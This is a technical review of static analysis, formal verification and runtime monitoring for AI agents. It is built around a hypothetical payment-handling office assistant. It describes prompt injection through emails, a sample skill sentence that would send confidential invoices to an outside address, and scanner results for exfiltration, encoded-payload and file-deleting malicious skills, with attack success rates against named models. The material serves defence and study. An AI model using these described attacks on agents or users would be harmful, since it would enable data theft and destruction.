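# Static Review and Runtime Verification for AI Agents That Choose Their Own Control Flow

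## The agent loop and the ways of checking software

Software assurance is the part of software engineering that looks for good grounds to trust a program. Much of it involves examining source code. Reviewers read the code, tools search it for known kinds of mistake, and for a few critical systems, engineers prove mathematically that no run can break a given rule. These methods rely on a programmer having written every branch a conventional program can take, so that the code contains, at least implicitly, everything the program can do.

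An AI agent is a language model (a program trained on very large amounts of text to produce text in response to a prompt) running in a loop with access to tools such as a file reader, a command line or a payment service. At each step the model picks the next tool call. The order of the steps, which programmers call control flow, is therefore decided during the run, and two runs of the same agent on the same request can differ.

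### The loop

An ordinary program, the harness, surrounds the model. It builds the prompt, calls the model, carries out tool calls and passes back the results. Bolin (2026), in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, describes the cycle in Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness first combines the user's request with standing instructions and a list of the available tools. The model generates a response to this prompt, which is either a final message for the user or a request for a tool call, for example to list the files in a folder. If it is a tool call, the harness executes it, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again. The cycle ends when the model produces a message instead of a tool call. In outline:

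```
history = instructions + tool list + user's request
repeat:
    output = model(history)
    if output is a final message: show it and stop
    result = run(output.tool, output.arguments)
    history = history + output + result
```

Other vendors' agents have much the same structure. According to GitHub's *The agent loop*, which documents Copilot CLI, each pass through the loop makes exactly one call to the model, which includes the full history of earlier tool calls and results.

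Anthropic's *How the agent loop works* gives a small example in which a developer asks an agent to fix the failing tests in one file. The agent runs the test suite, and three tests fail. It then reads two files, edits one, reruns the tests, which pass, and reports back. Nobody specified that sequence in advance, and the next steps would presumably have been different if the first run had turned up a missing library instead of three failures. Larger tasks involve dozens of tool calls, and Bolin says there could be hundreds in a single turn. Anthropic's development kit doesn't limit the number of turns unless the developer sets a limit.

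A model can take in only so much text at once, so when the conversation history grows too long, Codex replaces it with a shorter list of items. A check that depends on what happened two hundred steps ago therefore needs its own record of the run, because the shortened history may leave out the details of that step.

### Workflows and agents

Many products call a language model without giving it this much freedom. Anthropic's *Building effective agents* distinguishes workflows, in which predefined code paths coordinate the model and its tools, from agents, in which the model directs its own process. In a customer-service workflow, the model might classify each message as a refund request, a technical question or something else, and code would then send the message to one of three handlers. The model can still misclassify a message, but the code has only three branches, all written by a programmer,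 and a reviewer can read them all.

*LLM-as-Code* (Qi, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) illustrates the difference with a task that needs almost no planning: fetch eight web pages, summarize each one and write a report. A three-line loop in ordinary code visits each page exactly once. When the model drives the loop, it must decide at every turn which page to fetch next, whether to summarize yet and when to stop, and it may fetch the first page twice, skip the fifth or finish early. A language model draws its output from a probability distribution, so asking it what to do next amounts to what the paper calls "sampling a control-flow edge", where an edge is an arrow in the program's flowchart.

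Qi and colleagues argue that such errors compound, and that a stronger model slows the compounding but does not stop it. If we assume for simplicity that each decision is correct with probability *p*, independently of the others, a run of *n* decisions is entirely correct with probability *p*ⁿ. At 99% per decision, a run of 100 decisions has about a 37% chance of being entirely correct. This estimate is probably too low for agents that notice a mistake in a tool result and repair it, although the decision to repair is sampled from the same model and can also be wrong.

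Qi and colleagues propose writing any structure known in advance as code and calling the model only where the task needs judgment. On OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop-computer tasks, their agent succeeded on 86.8% of tasks within 15 steps, using Claude Sonnet 4.6. The public leaderboard lists 72.1% for the same model with up to 100 steps. This was not a controlled experiment, so differences other than whether code or the model controls the loop may explain part of the gap. Qi and colleagues also concede that a model-driven loop may suit exploratory work with no known structure, and Anthropic similarly recommends agents for open-ended problems where nobody can hardcode a path. In mixed designs, the program sets the maximum number of steps and the stopping conditions, and the model picks each step within those limits.

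### An office assistant under four rules

Suppose a company gives an employee an assistant of this kind to handle mail and small payments. It has five tools: `read_mail`, `read_file`, `ask_user` (which asks the employee a question and waits for the answer), `send_email` and `transfer_money`. The company sets four rules.

- R1: no transfer before the user confirms it.
- R2: transfers total at most $500 a day.
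- R3: no confidential text goes to an outside address.
- R4: a receipt eventually follows every payment.

R1 is a rule about order. R2 limits a running total, so the amount still allowed depends on what the assistant has already paid that day. R3 depends on the meaning of a text. R4 requires something to happen eventually after a payment but sets no deadline. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider mentions a closely related policy from electronic commerce that prohibits executions in which the customer pays and the seller never provides the service.

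Suppose the employee types "pay the caterer". In one run, the assistant reads the mail, finds an invoice for $180, asks for confirmation, transfers the money and emails a receipt. In another, the invoice isn't in the mailbox, so the assistant searches the files, finds two candidates and asks which one is right. With five tools, there are 5¹⁰ possible orders for ten calls, or nearly ten million, not counting different amounts, addresses and message texts. Outsiders can influence which order occurs, because the caterer's email becomes part of the history the model uses to choose its next step. An attacker can plant instructions in such an email, a technique known as prompt injection.

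### Traces and policies

A run's *trace* is the recorded sequence of its actions. The trace of the first run above is `read_mail`, `ask_user`, `transfer_money`, `send_email`, together with whatever details the harness logs for each call. Bartocci, Falcone and colleagues point out in *Introduction to Runtime Verification* that the choice of which events to record determines which properties anyone can describe. A log that lists the assistant's transfers without their amounts is useless for checking R2.

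A *policy* is a rule that defines which traces are acceptable, precisely enough to check. Schneider's standard example forbids a program from sending any message after it has read a file. "Handle payments sensibly" is not a policy in this sense, because two honest checkers could disagree about the same trace.

Computer scientists classify policies by how they can be violated, using definitions from Alpern and Schneider's *Defining Liveness* (1985). A *safety property* requires that some bad thing never happens. Formally, every trace that violates it has a finite beginning that no continuation can repair. First-come, first-served is a safety property because once a request has been served while an earlier one is still waiting, nothing that happens later can undo the violation. A *liveness property* requires that some good thing eventually happens. Formally, every finite trace has at least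 one continuation that satisfies the property. "The program eventually stops" is a liveness property, and a program that has been running for a week has not violated it, since it may still stop.

Many practical requirements combine safety and liveness. A sorting program should never return an unsorted list, which is a safety property, and it should eventually return something, which is a liveness property. Alpern and Schneider proved that every property of individual executions is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property. The distinction matters in practice because the two kinds of property require different proof techniques, and because a checker monitoring a run in progress can examine only a finite beginning of that run.

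Some policies raise a separate difficulty that the division does not address. They contain a *semantic predicate*, a condition that depends on what something means, such as "this text is confidential." Ordinary code can reliably compare an address with the company's domain name, but deciding whether a paragraph gives away an unannounced merger requires a human or machine judge, and both make mistakes.

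### What each method examines

Five methods of checking appear again and again in work on software assurance. They differ in their object and their timing.

| Method | What it examines | When |
|---|---|---|
| Code review | Code, configuration and written instructions, read by a person | Before release |
| Static analysis | The same material, or a graph extracted from it, read by a tool | Before release |
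| Formal proof | A mathematical description of the program and all its possible runs | Before release |
| Dry run | Traces of trial runs in an isolated environment | Before the real run |
| Runtime monitor | The trace of the real run | While the run unfolds, or afterwards from a log |

Human reviewers know what the software is for. *SA-11 Developer Testing and Evaluation*, a security control from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), recommends manual review for weaknesses that can't be found without understanding an application's requirements or context, an understanding that automated tools mostly lack. For instance, a reviewer who knows about R2 might notice that `transfer_money` accepts negative amounts, which would reduce the day's total.

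Static analysis gives up that understanding for speed and consistency. NIST describes tools that scan code for many kinds of vulnerability and for breaches of an organization's coding standards, and contrasts them with dynamic analysis, which runs the program on test cases. A static analysis is *sound* if it misses no violation of the property it checks. For example, a sound analysis for division by zero gives a clean report only when no input can cause such a division. Soundness comes with false alarms. The tool may flag a line that is harmless because an earlier check has already ruled out zero. *Agentproof* (2026) applies static analysis to language-model software by extracting a workflow's graph from the source code and checking properties that do not depend on what text the model generates. It is harder to determine how far such analysis reaches when the model itself picks the next step.

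Formal proof aims at the strongest conclusion, that every possible run satisfies the property. Engineers reach it either by theorem proving, which works like a proof in mathematics, or by model checking, in which a program searches all the runs of a model with finitely many states. They can prove properties of the software around a language model instead of the language model itself. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) presents machine-checked theorems about an interpreter, the harness program that calls the language model, and the guarantee applies to every agent written in the paper's programming language. The proof covers only the property stated in the theorem. Leucker and Schallhart (2008) caution more generally in *A Brief Account of Runtime Verification* that proofs often refer to a model of the real system, and that the implementation may behave slightly differently.

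A dry run samples actual runs instead of reasoning about possible ones. The company could give the office assistant a copy of the mailbox and a pretend bank account and see what it does. Anthropic advises extensive testing of agents in such sandboxed environments. The evidence is concrete but covers only the runs that took place, and the assistant may choose different steps when it works with the real mailbox and bank account.

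Leucker and Schallhart define a runtime monitor as a device that reads a finite trace of an actual run and yields a verdict. They argue for at least three verdicts: true, false and inconclusive. Under the rule that nothing bad may happen before a program has initialized, for example, the verdict is permanently false if the bad event comes first and permanently true if initialization comes first. Until one of them occurs, the monitor should report "inconclusive." A monitor needs no description of the program's internals, which makes runtime verification attractive for language models. Koohestani (2025) writes in *AgentGuard* that runtime verification cannot prove properties of unobserved paths but can give strong guarantees about the execution that actually occurred.

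A monitor by itself only reports. A *gate* is a monitor that can also stop or replace an action before it takes effect. Anthropic's development kit supports gates through hooks, which are pieces of code that can modify or block a tool call before it runs. A gate can make two kinds of error. When enforcing R3, it might let through an email that paraphrases a secret contract, which is a *miss*, or stop a public price list because the word "confidential" remains in an old footer, which is a *false block*. Neither error necessarily ends the run. After a block, the model receives a rejection message as the tool's result and typically tries another approach, so the gate also affects the rest of the trace.

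Researchers were interested in checking software during execution before language-model agents existed. In 2008, Leucker and Schallhart considered software services that act as autonomous agents under contracts with one another, and judged it "next to impossible" to analyze such systems before execution. In *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026) reviewed 38 studies on specifying, verifying and enforcing the safety of language-model agents. They found that runtime monitoring is the most mature enforcement strategy, but that its guarantees cover only single steps or short stretches of a run. They also rated the certainty of the evidence as very low for seven of the field's nine main claims.

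The company deploying the office assistant wants to know, before handing over the payment tool, which claims about the assistant it can settle before the assistant runs, which it can settle only during the run, and which it can't settle at all.

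## What static analysis can say when a model picks the next step

If a programmer had written every branch of the office assistant, the company could settle R1, no transfer before the user confirms it, by tracing every route through the code. The payment routine might look like this:

```
1  invoice = find_invoice()
2  if invoice.amount > 0:
3      if ask_user(invoice) == "yes":
4          transfer_money(invoice)
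5  send_email(report)
```

A static analyser turns such code into a *control-flow graph*, with a node for each statement and an edge from each statement to every statement that could run next. Line 2 has edges to lines 3 and 5, and line 3 has edges to lines 4 and 5. Three paths lead from top to bottom, and the only one that reaches the transfer requires the user to say "yes" first. R1 therefore holds on every run.

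The graph usually contains more paths than the program can take. For example, `find_invoice` may never return an amount of zero or less, in which case no run follows the edge from line 2 to line 5. An analyser that can't prove this keeps the edge. This *over-approximation* is how static analysis achieves soundness. If *R* is the set of real runs and *P* the set of paths in the graph, the analyser ensures *R* ⊆ *P*, so if no path in *P* breaks the rule, no real run does either. The analyser raises an alarm when some path in *P* breaks the rule, and the alarm is false if that path lies outside *R*.

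### A graph that joins every tool to every other

Suppose a harness offers 12 tools and stops after 20 calls, and the model may pick any tool at any step. There are 12²⁰ possible tool sequences, about 3.8 × 10²¹, not counting different arguments to each tool.

Graph algorithms can handle that many paths because they don't list them one by one. The graph has only 12 nodes and 144 edges, counting the edge from each tool to itself, so a laptop can search it instantly. The problem is that the code allows the tools to be called in any order, so the only sound graph connects every tool to every other. For any two tools A and B, it contains a path on which B comes first. An analyser checking R1 on this graph will report a possible violation however careful the model is, because the graph doesn't depend on the model.

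Strictly speaking, the alarm may not be false. A language model gives some probability to almost every continuation, unless the sampling settings cut off the unlikely ones, so a run that pays before asking is usually possible, if improbable. A control-flow graph only separates possible runs from impossible ones. It can still rule out actions that no tool on the agent's list can perform. For example, no run can move money if the agent has no payment tool and no other tool, such as a command line, that could make a payment.

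Analysers built for agents work within this limit. *AgentFlow* (2026) extracts a dependency graph from agent programs, over-approximating the behavior that a program's structure permits rather than predicting a single trace. The more the developer has restricted which tools each agent holds and which agents can hand work to each other, the more informative the graph is. *AgentRaft* (2026), which looks for agents that expose too much data, uses a language model to discard dependencies that look spurious, so that its graph keeps only tool combinations that make sense together. The smaller graph is a better guide for testing, but if the model wrongly discards a dependency, the analysis no longer covers it, and an attacker's email might steer the agent along that path.

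### The older problem of `eval` and reflection

Programmers faced a milder version of this problem long before language models. JavaScript's `eval` runs a piece of text as code, and reflection in Java lets a program look up a function by a name computed at run time. A static analyser often can't determine the text or the name from the source. An agent's harness does much the same thing in its main loop, where the model outputs a tool's name and the harness looks up and calls the function with that name. If one of the tools is a Python interpreter, the harness also runs model-written text as code, just as `eval` does.

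As *In Defense of Soundiness* (Livshits, Sridharan et al., 2015) explains, a sound analyser would have to assume that `eval` can do anything, which tends to make the results too imprecise to use and too large to compute. Many tools therefore assume that `eval` does nothing unless they can work out its argument in advance. Livshits and colleagues coined the word *soundy* for analyses that over-approximate most of a language but deliberately ignore a few features well known to experts. They knew of no realistic whole-program tool that avoided unsound choices altogether. They accepted this because many users can tolerate some unsoundness, but they asked researchers to state the exceptions openly and check how heavily real programs rely on them. An agent relies on the model's choices for nearly everything it does, so an analysis that is sound except for those choices covers little beyond the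 harness.

These gaps can be large even in ordinary software. In *Call Graph Soundness in Android Static Analysis*, Samhi, Just and colleagues (2024) ran 13 static tools on 1,000 Android apps, then ran the apps and logged every method (a named unit of code) that executed. On average, the static tools missed 61% of the methods that ran. The comparison between tools covers only the 126 apps that every tool could process, which were probably among the simplest. Five minutes of random input exercised only 8% of the methods in an average app, so Samhi and colleagues regard the measured gap as a lower bound.

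More precise algorithms missed more of the methods that apps actually executed. In FlowDroid, a widely used tool for finding data leaks, the most precise algorithm missed an average of 1,965 executed methods per app, and the least precise missed 1,294. Each algorithm is supposed to remove only paths that can't occur, but the more precise ones also removed paths that did. One major cause was methods that Android or an outside framework calls without any call in the app's code. An agent's harness calls its registered tools in the same way.

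### Undecidable in theory, finite in practice

Shi, Du and colleagues (2025) go further in *SoK*, a survey of trust and authorization in agent systems. They argue that agent behavior is undecidable, meaning that no algorithm can determine in advance whether an agent will break a security rule. Their argument rests on two classical results. In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no program can solve the *halting problem*, which is to decide, for every program and every input, whether the program eventually stops on that input. *Rice's theorem* (1953) extends this result to nearly every question about a program's behavior. Let *C* be a set of programs defined purely by what they compute, so that two programs with identical behavior are either both in *C* or both outside it. An algorithm can decide membership in *C* only if *C* contains all programs or none. *LLMs versus the Halting Problem* (2026)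 lists memory safety and program equivalence among the central verification tasks that fall under the theorem.

*The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic* (2026) reproduces the short proof. It starts with a program *q* that has the property and assumes that a program that never outputs anything lacks it. (If that program has the property, the same argument works with a *q* that lacks it.) For any program *M* and input *w*, we can write a new program that runs *M* on *w* and, if *M* stops, then behaves like *q*. The new program has the property exactly when *M* stops on *w*, so an algorithm that could decide the property would also solve the halting problem.

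Shi and colleagues apply the same construction to agents. They take an agent with external memory and repeated tool use to be Turing-complete, meaning it can carry out any computation. They then imagine an agent instructed to simulate *M* on *w* and to carry out a forbidden deletion if and only if *M* halts. A perfect verifier of agents would have to determine whether *M* halts.

This version assumes that the model follows its instructions faithfully through a simulation of any length, which is a strong assumption for a system that samples its output. Franco and Gershenson (2026), in *Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified*, avoid it by having a tool do the computation instead of the model. Their agent asks a computer to run a program *p* and, if *p* returns, asks it to run a dangerous program *q*. Deciding whether even this simple agent is safe requires deciding whether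 *p* halts. They also show that any algorithm that labels every agent safe or unsafe will mislabel an agent that applies the algorithm to itself and does the opposite of what the label predicts. In their construction, the difficulty comes from the agent's ability to run arbitrary code, which the office assistant lacks because none of its five tools is an interpreter.

All these results concern one algorithm that must be right about every agent. They do not rule out proofs about particular agents, and Shi and colleagues note that an agent that does nothing is always safe. Nor do they rule out analysers that sometimes raise false alarms. *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) cites an earlier theorem by Hamlen and colleagues that static analysis can exactly enforce a property of programs if and only if the property is decidable. The theorem does not cover over-approximation,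 which gives up exactness. Undecidable problems are also often manageable on the programs people actually write. In the tests reported in *LLMs versus the Halting Problem*, frontier language models came close to specialized analysers in predicting whether concrete programs terminate, although they were much weaker at constructing valid proofs of it.

The theorems also assume unlimited time and memory, which no deployed agent has. If the harness caps the number of steps, the context has a maximum length, and every tool has a time limit and returns a bounded result, then the agent and its tools can be in only finitely many states, and a program could in principle check them all. Franco and Gershenson show that limiting only the length of the user's request would not be enough, because a tool might still run forever. They prove that when context, values and running time are all bounded, safety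 is decidable but PSPACE-complete, even for a checker that has the agent's full description. PSPACE-complete problems are the hardest of those solvable with memory that grows only polynomially with the size of the problem, and every known method for them takes exponential time in the worst case.

"Undecidable" is therefore the wrong word for the office assistant, but analysing it is not much easier in practice. Static analysers can handle enormous numbers of possible states when source code sorts them into groups. A conventional program with a single kilobyte of memory has about 10²⁴⁶⁶ possible states, but a line such as `if amount > 500` treats a huge number of inputs alike, so the analyser can reason about all of them at once. If the assistant's context holds 100,000 tokens (word fragments), each from a vocabulary of 100,000, there are 10⁵⁰⁰⁰⁰⁰ possible full contexts, and the model's weights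 are billions of numbers with no such line to group them. Together with the code that runs the model, the weights fully determine how likely each output is, but nobody knows how to work out from them which emails lead to a transfer. A company that rents the model through a provider's interface usually doesn't have the weights.

### What a fixed graph proves

Static analysis is more effective for workflows, where the developer fixes the order of steps and the model does the work inside each one. The developer defines this order as a graph in the code, so a tool can extract it from the source, as *Automated Safety Analysis for Agentic Workflows* (2026) points out. Static analysis also works on other things that are complete before they are used, such as an installed skill, a program the model has just written or a permission policy.

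*Agentproof* extracts such graphs from four frameworks that describe workflows in incompatible ways (LangGraph, CrewAI, AutoGen and Google's Agent Development Kit). Each node in the resulting typed graph has a kind, such as model call, tool, router or human step, and each edge is direct, conditional, parallel or a loop. *Agentproof* then runs six structural checks on the graph.

| Check | What the graph must satisfy |
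|---|---|
| Exit reachability | A path leads from the entry to every exit |
| No traps | From every reachable node, some path leads to an exit |
| No dead ends | Every node except an exit has an outgoing edge |
| Router shape | Every edge out of a router is conditional |
| Human step | The graph contains a human step; a stricter option requires one on every path to a sensitive tool |
| Tool declaration | Every tool node names its tools |

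When a check fails, the tool generally prints a path that violates it. One test workflow sorts incoming emails and drafts replies to the normal-priority ones, but no edge leads from the drafting step to the sending step. The printed path runs from the start through the classifier and the router to the drafting step, where the workflow gets stuck. A trial run would reveal this bug only if it included a normal-priority email.

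To check rules about order, *Agentproof* also translates each rule into a finite automaton, which reads events one at a time and moves between a few states. For example, a rule might say that a review must follow each draft before the next draft begins. Its automaton has the states "idle", "waiting for review" and "violated". A draft moves it from "idle" to "waiting for review", and a second draft before the review moves it to "violated". The tool pairs workflow nodes with automaton states and searches the pairs, starting from the entry node and "idle". At each edge, it moves to the next node and updates the automaton. If the search reaches "violated", the tool can reconstruct the path that breaks the rule. Otherwise, no path breaks the rule, however many times the workflow repeats its loops. The search can cover every path because *V* nodes and *Q* automaton states make only *V* × *Q* pairs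 to explore.

The tool's developers evaluated it on 18 small workflows, of 5 to 12 nodes each, that they wrote with deliberate defects. Five had structural defects and ten had no human step, although some of those ten handle low-risk tasks that may not need one. The search of node and state pairs also found a missing review step that did not show up in ten random simulated runs of the same workflow. These results show that the tool finds the defects it looks for, but they don't measure how common those defects are in real products. The structural checks took about 105 milliseconds on artificial graphs of 5,000 nodes, so speed is not a constraint.

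### R1 with and without a fixed confirmation

The company could build the office assistant's payment function in two ways:

```
Fixed:  entry → read_mail → model drafts payment → user confirms
              → transfer_money → send_email → exit
        (if the user declines, the workflow goes straight to exit)

Free:   entry → model ⇄ any of the five tools
        (the model decides when to exit)
```

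R1 fits the stricter form of *Agentproof*'s human-step check, which deletes every human step from the graph and tests whether any path from the entry still reaches a sensitive tool. *Agentproof* can't express R1 as an ordinary order rule because its rule language can't refer to the past. One of its sample policies, labeled as deployment approval, actually requires an approval after a deployment and before the next one.

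In the fixed design, deleting the confirmation disconnects the graph, so the search stops at the drafted payment and the check passes. This guarantee holds whatever the model writes in its draft, and even if the caterer's email contains planted instructions, because text in an email can't add an edge to the graph.

In the free design, deleting `ask_user` still leaves a path from the entry through the model to `transfer_money`, so the check fails. The alarm is correct because nothing in the code stops the assistant from paying without asking. Adding a sentence to the prompt that tells the model to ask first would not change the graph. The company could instead build the confirmation into the transfer tool, so that every call goes to the user first and then to the bank. If the extracted graph shows that confirmation as a human step, the check passes again, and the model can still choose everything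 else.

Even a pass proves slightly less than R1, because it shows only that at least one human step precedes any transfer. If the workflow loops from one transfer straight to another, a single confirmation satisfies the check for both. A second search that starts from the transfer node would catch this. The check also doesn't establish that the user said yes, or that the amount the user saw is the amount the bank receives. In LangGraph workflows, the tool by default recognizes human steps by the word "human" in their names, so a careless name can hide a real confirmation or suggest one that isn't there. If the program changes its own graph during the run, the result no longer applies. The tool also treats every conditional edge as passable, and nobody has measured how many false alarms this causes.

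*Agentproof* handles the assistant's other rules less well. It can't express R2, the daily limit, because its events include a tool's name but not the amount of a payment. The events also don't capture what a text means, which R3 depends on. The language can only approximate R4, by requiring a receipt after each payment either before the next payment or within a fixed number of steps. A run that makes one payment and never sends a receipt doesn't violate the first version, and the second imposes a deadline that R4 doesn't contain.

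### Loops and their limits

A cap on the number of steps is one of the few useful properties that code can guarantee for an agent that chooses its own steps, because the harness controls the loop. *λ_A* (Liu, 2026) translates agent configuration files into a form of lambda calculus, a minimal notation that builds programs out of functions. A loop with a cap of *n* becomes a function that can call itself at most *n* times. Liu proved by induction that such a loop ends within *n* rounds, whatever the model outputs, and checked the proof with the proof assistant Coq. With a cap of 0 the loop returns at once, and with a higher cap it runs one round and then passes control to a loop with a cap of *n* − 1. The theorem assumes that each model call and each tool call ends, so a tool that hangs can still stall the agent. The cap also limits cost by limiting the number of calls. A research agent with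 a cap of 20 rounds, each with one model call and one tool call, can make at most 40 calls, and in Liu's test it made 15.

Liu also built a linter, a tool that flags suspicious code, and ran it on 835 agent configurations from GitHub. It marked 94.1% of them as structurally incomplete, for example because they named no model or gave the agent no way to stop. That figure is a poor measure of how many were faulty, because only 27 of the 50 reported errors that Liu checked by hand were real, a precision of 54%. In nearly all the other cases, Python code elsewhere in the repository supplied the missing piece. When the linter could also read that code, precision rose to 96% on the same sample and 100% on a larger one. An agent's program is often spread over several files, so much of it will seem to be missing if a reviewer checks only the configuration file.

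In *When Agents Do Not Stop*, Hou, Wang and colleagues (2026) searched for loops without an effective cap, which they call infinite agentic loops. Their analyser, IAL-Scan, builds a graph of an agent project and checks whether each cycle in it can repeat a costly step, such as a model call, without a firm limit. A condition such as "stop when the model requests no more tools" doesn't count as a limit, because it depends on the model's output. A cap on an inner agent doesn't count either if an outer loop can keep restarting that agent. For example, when the model in a virtual assistant published by NVIDIA returns an empty answer, the code adds a message asking for a real output and calls the model again. There is no maximum number of attempts, and the history gets slightly longer each time.

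Across 6,549 repositories, IAL-Scan reported 74 loops. Manual review confirmed 68 of them in 47 projects, a precision of 91.9%. Most of the six false alarms involved caps that were hard to see in the code, such as a framework's default of three iterations. The tool is not sound. Hou and colleagues found seven failures it had missed by reviewing code that language models had flagged independently, and there may be others. It misses failures partly because a language model discards most of the candidates found by the graph analysis. In three repeated runs, the graph analysis gave the same 340 candidates, but those left after filtering included 68, 64 and 60 of the confirmed failures. Without the filter, reviewers would have had 272 false alarms to go through. IAL-Scan also doesn't cover every kind of wasted effort. An agent that repeats a useless search 50 times under a cap of 50 has an effective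 limit, so it falls outside what the tool looks for.

### Conditions on each model step

Graph checks treat a model call as a node that could output anything. To try to prove more, *Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) gives each step a precondition, which states what must hold before the step, and a postcondition, which states what the step should establish. For example, a step that extracts an invoice might require the text of an email and have to produce a record with an amount and a payee. A program written in Lean 4, a language for machine-checked proofs, verifies that earlier steps establish everything a later step requires. In one software-repair workflow, the verifier found a testing step that needed evidence from an earlier repair step, although the harness ran each step without access to the previous conversation. The instructions mention the evidence as if it were available,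 so a person reading them could easily overlook the problem.

These proofs rest on an assumption that Wang and colleagues call *LLMExec*, which formally states that for every starting context that meets a step's preconditions, there exists some output of the model that meets its postconditions. Even if we grant this for every step, the proof shows only that the workflow is coherent and could succeed. It doesn't show that every run will succeed, whereas a sound analysis draws conclusions that hold for all runs. A separate layer of the system later checks recorded traces to see whether the steps actually met their conditions.

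Workflows that passed verification performed better. Wang and colleagues had a language model write 40 workflows, and for each of two benchmarks they compared three that passed with three that failed, using five models. On 50 hard software-repair tasks, the passing workflows solved 58.27% and the failing ones 43.47%, a difference of 14.80 points. On 100 questions about AI research papers, the difference was 9.07 points. Each group had only three workflows, and those that passed also tended to have better retry loops, so it is hard to tell how much of the gain comes from the specific defects the verifier detects. Verified workflows still failed on about two in five tasks in the easier benchmark. A language model also wrote the conditions, and a manual check found that 36 of 1,460 (2.47%) were wrong, although correcting them changed none of the verdicts.

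Replacing *LLMExec* with a theorem would require proving something about the neural network itself. *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025) reports that eight teams competed to verify neural networks on 16 regular and 9 extended benchmarks. A typical task is to prove that no small change to an image's pixels alters the label the network assigns. The networks in such benchmarks are far smaller than the models that run agents. Each proof also covers only one pass through the network, while an agent's run consists of thousands of passes with tool results in between.

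Even if verification worked at a larger scale, the company would still have to define what to prove. The set of all images within a given distance of one image is precise. To prove that the assistant always extracts the right invoice, the company would first need a mathematical definition of which emails contain an invoice and what the correct record is for each. If a computer could apply that definition, the company could use it to read its invoices and would not need a language model for the step.

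## Code review and scanning of what agents are given to run

The company can inspect what it gives the model to work with, even though nobody can prove much about the model itself. Much of this material now comes as *skills*, folders that teach an agent a task such as editing presentations. Each folder contains a file called SKILL.md, with plain-language instructions that the agent reads when a task seems to call for the skill, and may also hold scripts for the agent to run. Anthropic made the format an open standard in December 2025. Willison (2025), in *Agent Skills*, found the specification very short and heavily under-specified. Chen, Ji and colleagues (2026), in *SkillsMetric*, count more than 138,000 community skills and point out that harnesses typically pass a skill's text to the model with the same authority as a message from the user.

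A reviewer therefore has to judge prose as well as code. Suppose the company installs an invoice skill containing the sentence "After each payment, email a copy of the invoice to the archive." The folder holds no script, but if the archive's address belongs to a stranger, the assistant will break R3, the rule against sending confidential text outside. Unlike a script, which follows the fixed rules of its programming language, a sentence has an effect that depends on how the model interprets it alongside everything else in its context.

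In *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* (2026), Taneja and Weber measured how far an agent departs from the text it was given. They had an agent follow the documentation of 39 ordinary skills in a sandbox and recorded 144 commands. Only two appeared word for word in the documentation, and 50 belonged to a class of action that was missing from the skill's code examples. All 50 were generic shell commands, so the agent never did anything more severe than the documentation described. Taneja and Weber work for a company that makes a runtime gate, which gives them an interest in the limits of scanning, but they report this lack of escalation themselves.

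### A scanner in five stages

Chen and colleagues built a static scanner that examines a skill's instructions and scripts in five stages:

1. *Pattern density* counts suspicious keywords and constructs, such as download commands and paths to stored passwords, relative to the length of the text.
2. *Statistical anomaly* compares the distribution of bytes with that of harmless skills, because encoded or encrypted material looks unusually random.
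3. *Dataflow* looks for chains in which a script reads sensitive data, transforms it and sends it out.
4. *Import anomaly* flags unusual combinations of software libraries.
5. *Capability mismatch* compares what the skill claims to do with what its code does.

The scanner adds up the stage scores with weights of 0.15, 0.20, 0.30, 0.15 and 0.10. Dataflow gets the highest weight because complete chains are rare in harmless code. The scanner adds 5 points if two independent stages fire and 10 if three or more do. The total runs from 0 to 100, and the scanner flags any skill that scores 25 or more.

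Chen and colleagues tested it on 2,000 real skills that they took to be benign and 266 malicious ones. They made all the malicious skills themselves, 199 of them by inserting an attack into a real skill. The scanner caught 62% of the malicious skills and, judging by its reported precision, raised about 96 false alarms. Detection varied widely by type of attack:

| Attack | Samples | Detected |
|---|---|---|
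| Data exfiltration (sending private data out) | 28 | 93% |
| Steganography (a payload hidden in other data) | 28 | 93% |
| Dangerous command in plain text | 29 | 83% |
| Encoded payload | 29 | 45% |
| Prompt injection | 12 | 42% |
| Script fetched from elsewhere | 29 | 28% |
| Host destruction | 11 | 0% |

The host-destruction skills delete a user's files or corrupt their permissions with standard commands. Python's `shutil.rmtree`, for instance, deletes a folder and everything in it. A build tool calls it to clear temporary files, but an attacker can call it on a user's projects folder. No stage flags the attack, because the script contacts no server, imports nothing unusual and contains no encoded text. Flagging every deletion command would give reviewers too many false alarms, since harmless scripts use them so often. A rule about particular folders would help a little, but some users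 do want an old project deleted. A reviewer can't tell cleanup from damage by reading the skill alone, because it doesn't show what is in the folder or whether the user wants to keep it.

Prompt injection escapes detection for a similar reason. The scanner's code-oriented stages have almost nothing to measure in pure prose, and the injected skills it caught contained code blocks.

The percentages for small categories are rough. A scanner that catches 20% of host-destruction attacks on average would still miss all 11 about 9% of the time, although the design of the stages is enough to explain the zero here. Inserted attacks may also be easier to spot than those of a determined attacker. When Chen and colleagues ran the scanner on the SKILL.md files of 138,133 public skills, it flagged 1.75%. The top-scoring ones were mostly legitimate security tools, which need dangerous-looking code to work.

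### Scanners that use a language model

Scanners that use a language model can read the prose that scanners using fixed patterns miss. *AgentTrap* (Zhuang, Xing and colleagues, 2026) compared both kinds on the skills from 91 malicious and 50 harmless tasks. Ten of the malicious tasks used skills from a public registry, and the researchers built the other 81 by adding attacks to popular skills.

| Scanner | Malicious flagged (of 91) | Harmless flagged (of 50) |
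|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal, which pools antivirus engines | 0 | 0 |
| Cisco, rules only | 26 | 5 |
| MalBench, rules only | 31 | 7 |
| MalBench, rules and a language model | 44 | 3 |
| SkillScan, rules and a language model | 50 | 4 |
| AgentTrap's own model-based reviewer | 80 | 2 |

The strongest outside scanner missed 41 malicious tasks, even with a language model's help. AgentTrap's reviewer uses GPT-5.4-mini to judge whether the skill would cause unsafe behavior during an ordinary task, which catches attacks disguised as routine steps. Its lead over the outside scanners is probably somewhat inflated, because the team that wrote its instructions also built most of the attacks. The misses matter because agents often follow a malicious skill's instructions. With only basic tools, Kimi K2.6 carried out 75 of the 91 attacks and Claude Sonnet 4.6 carried out 17.

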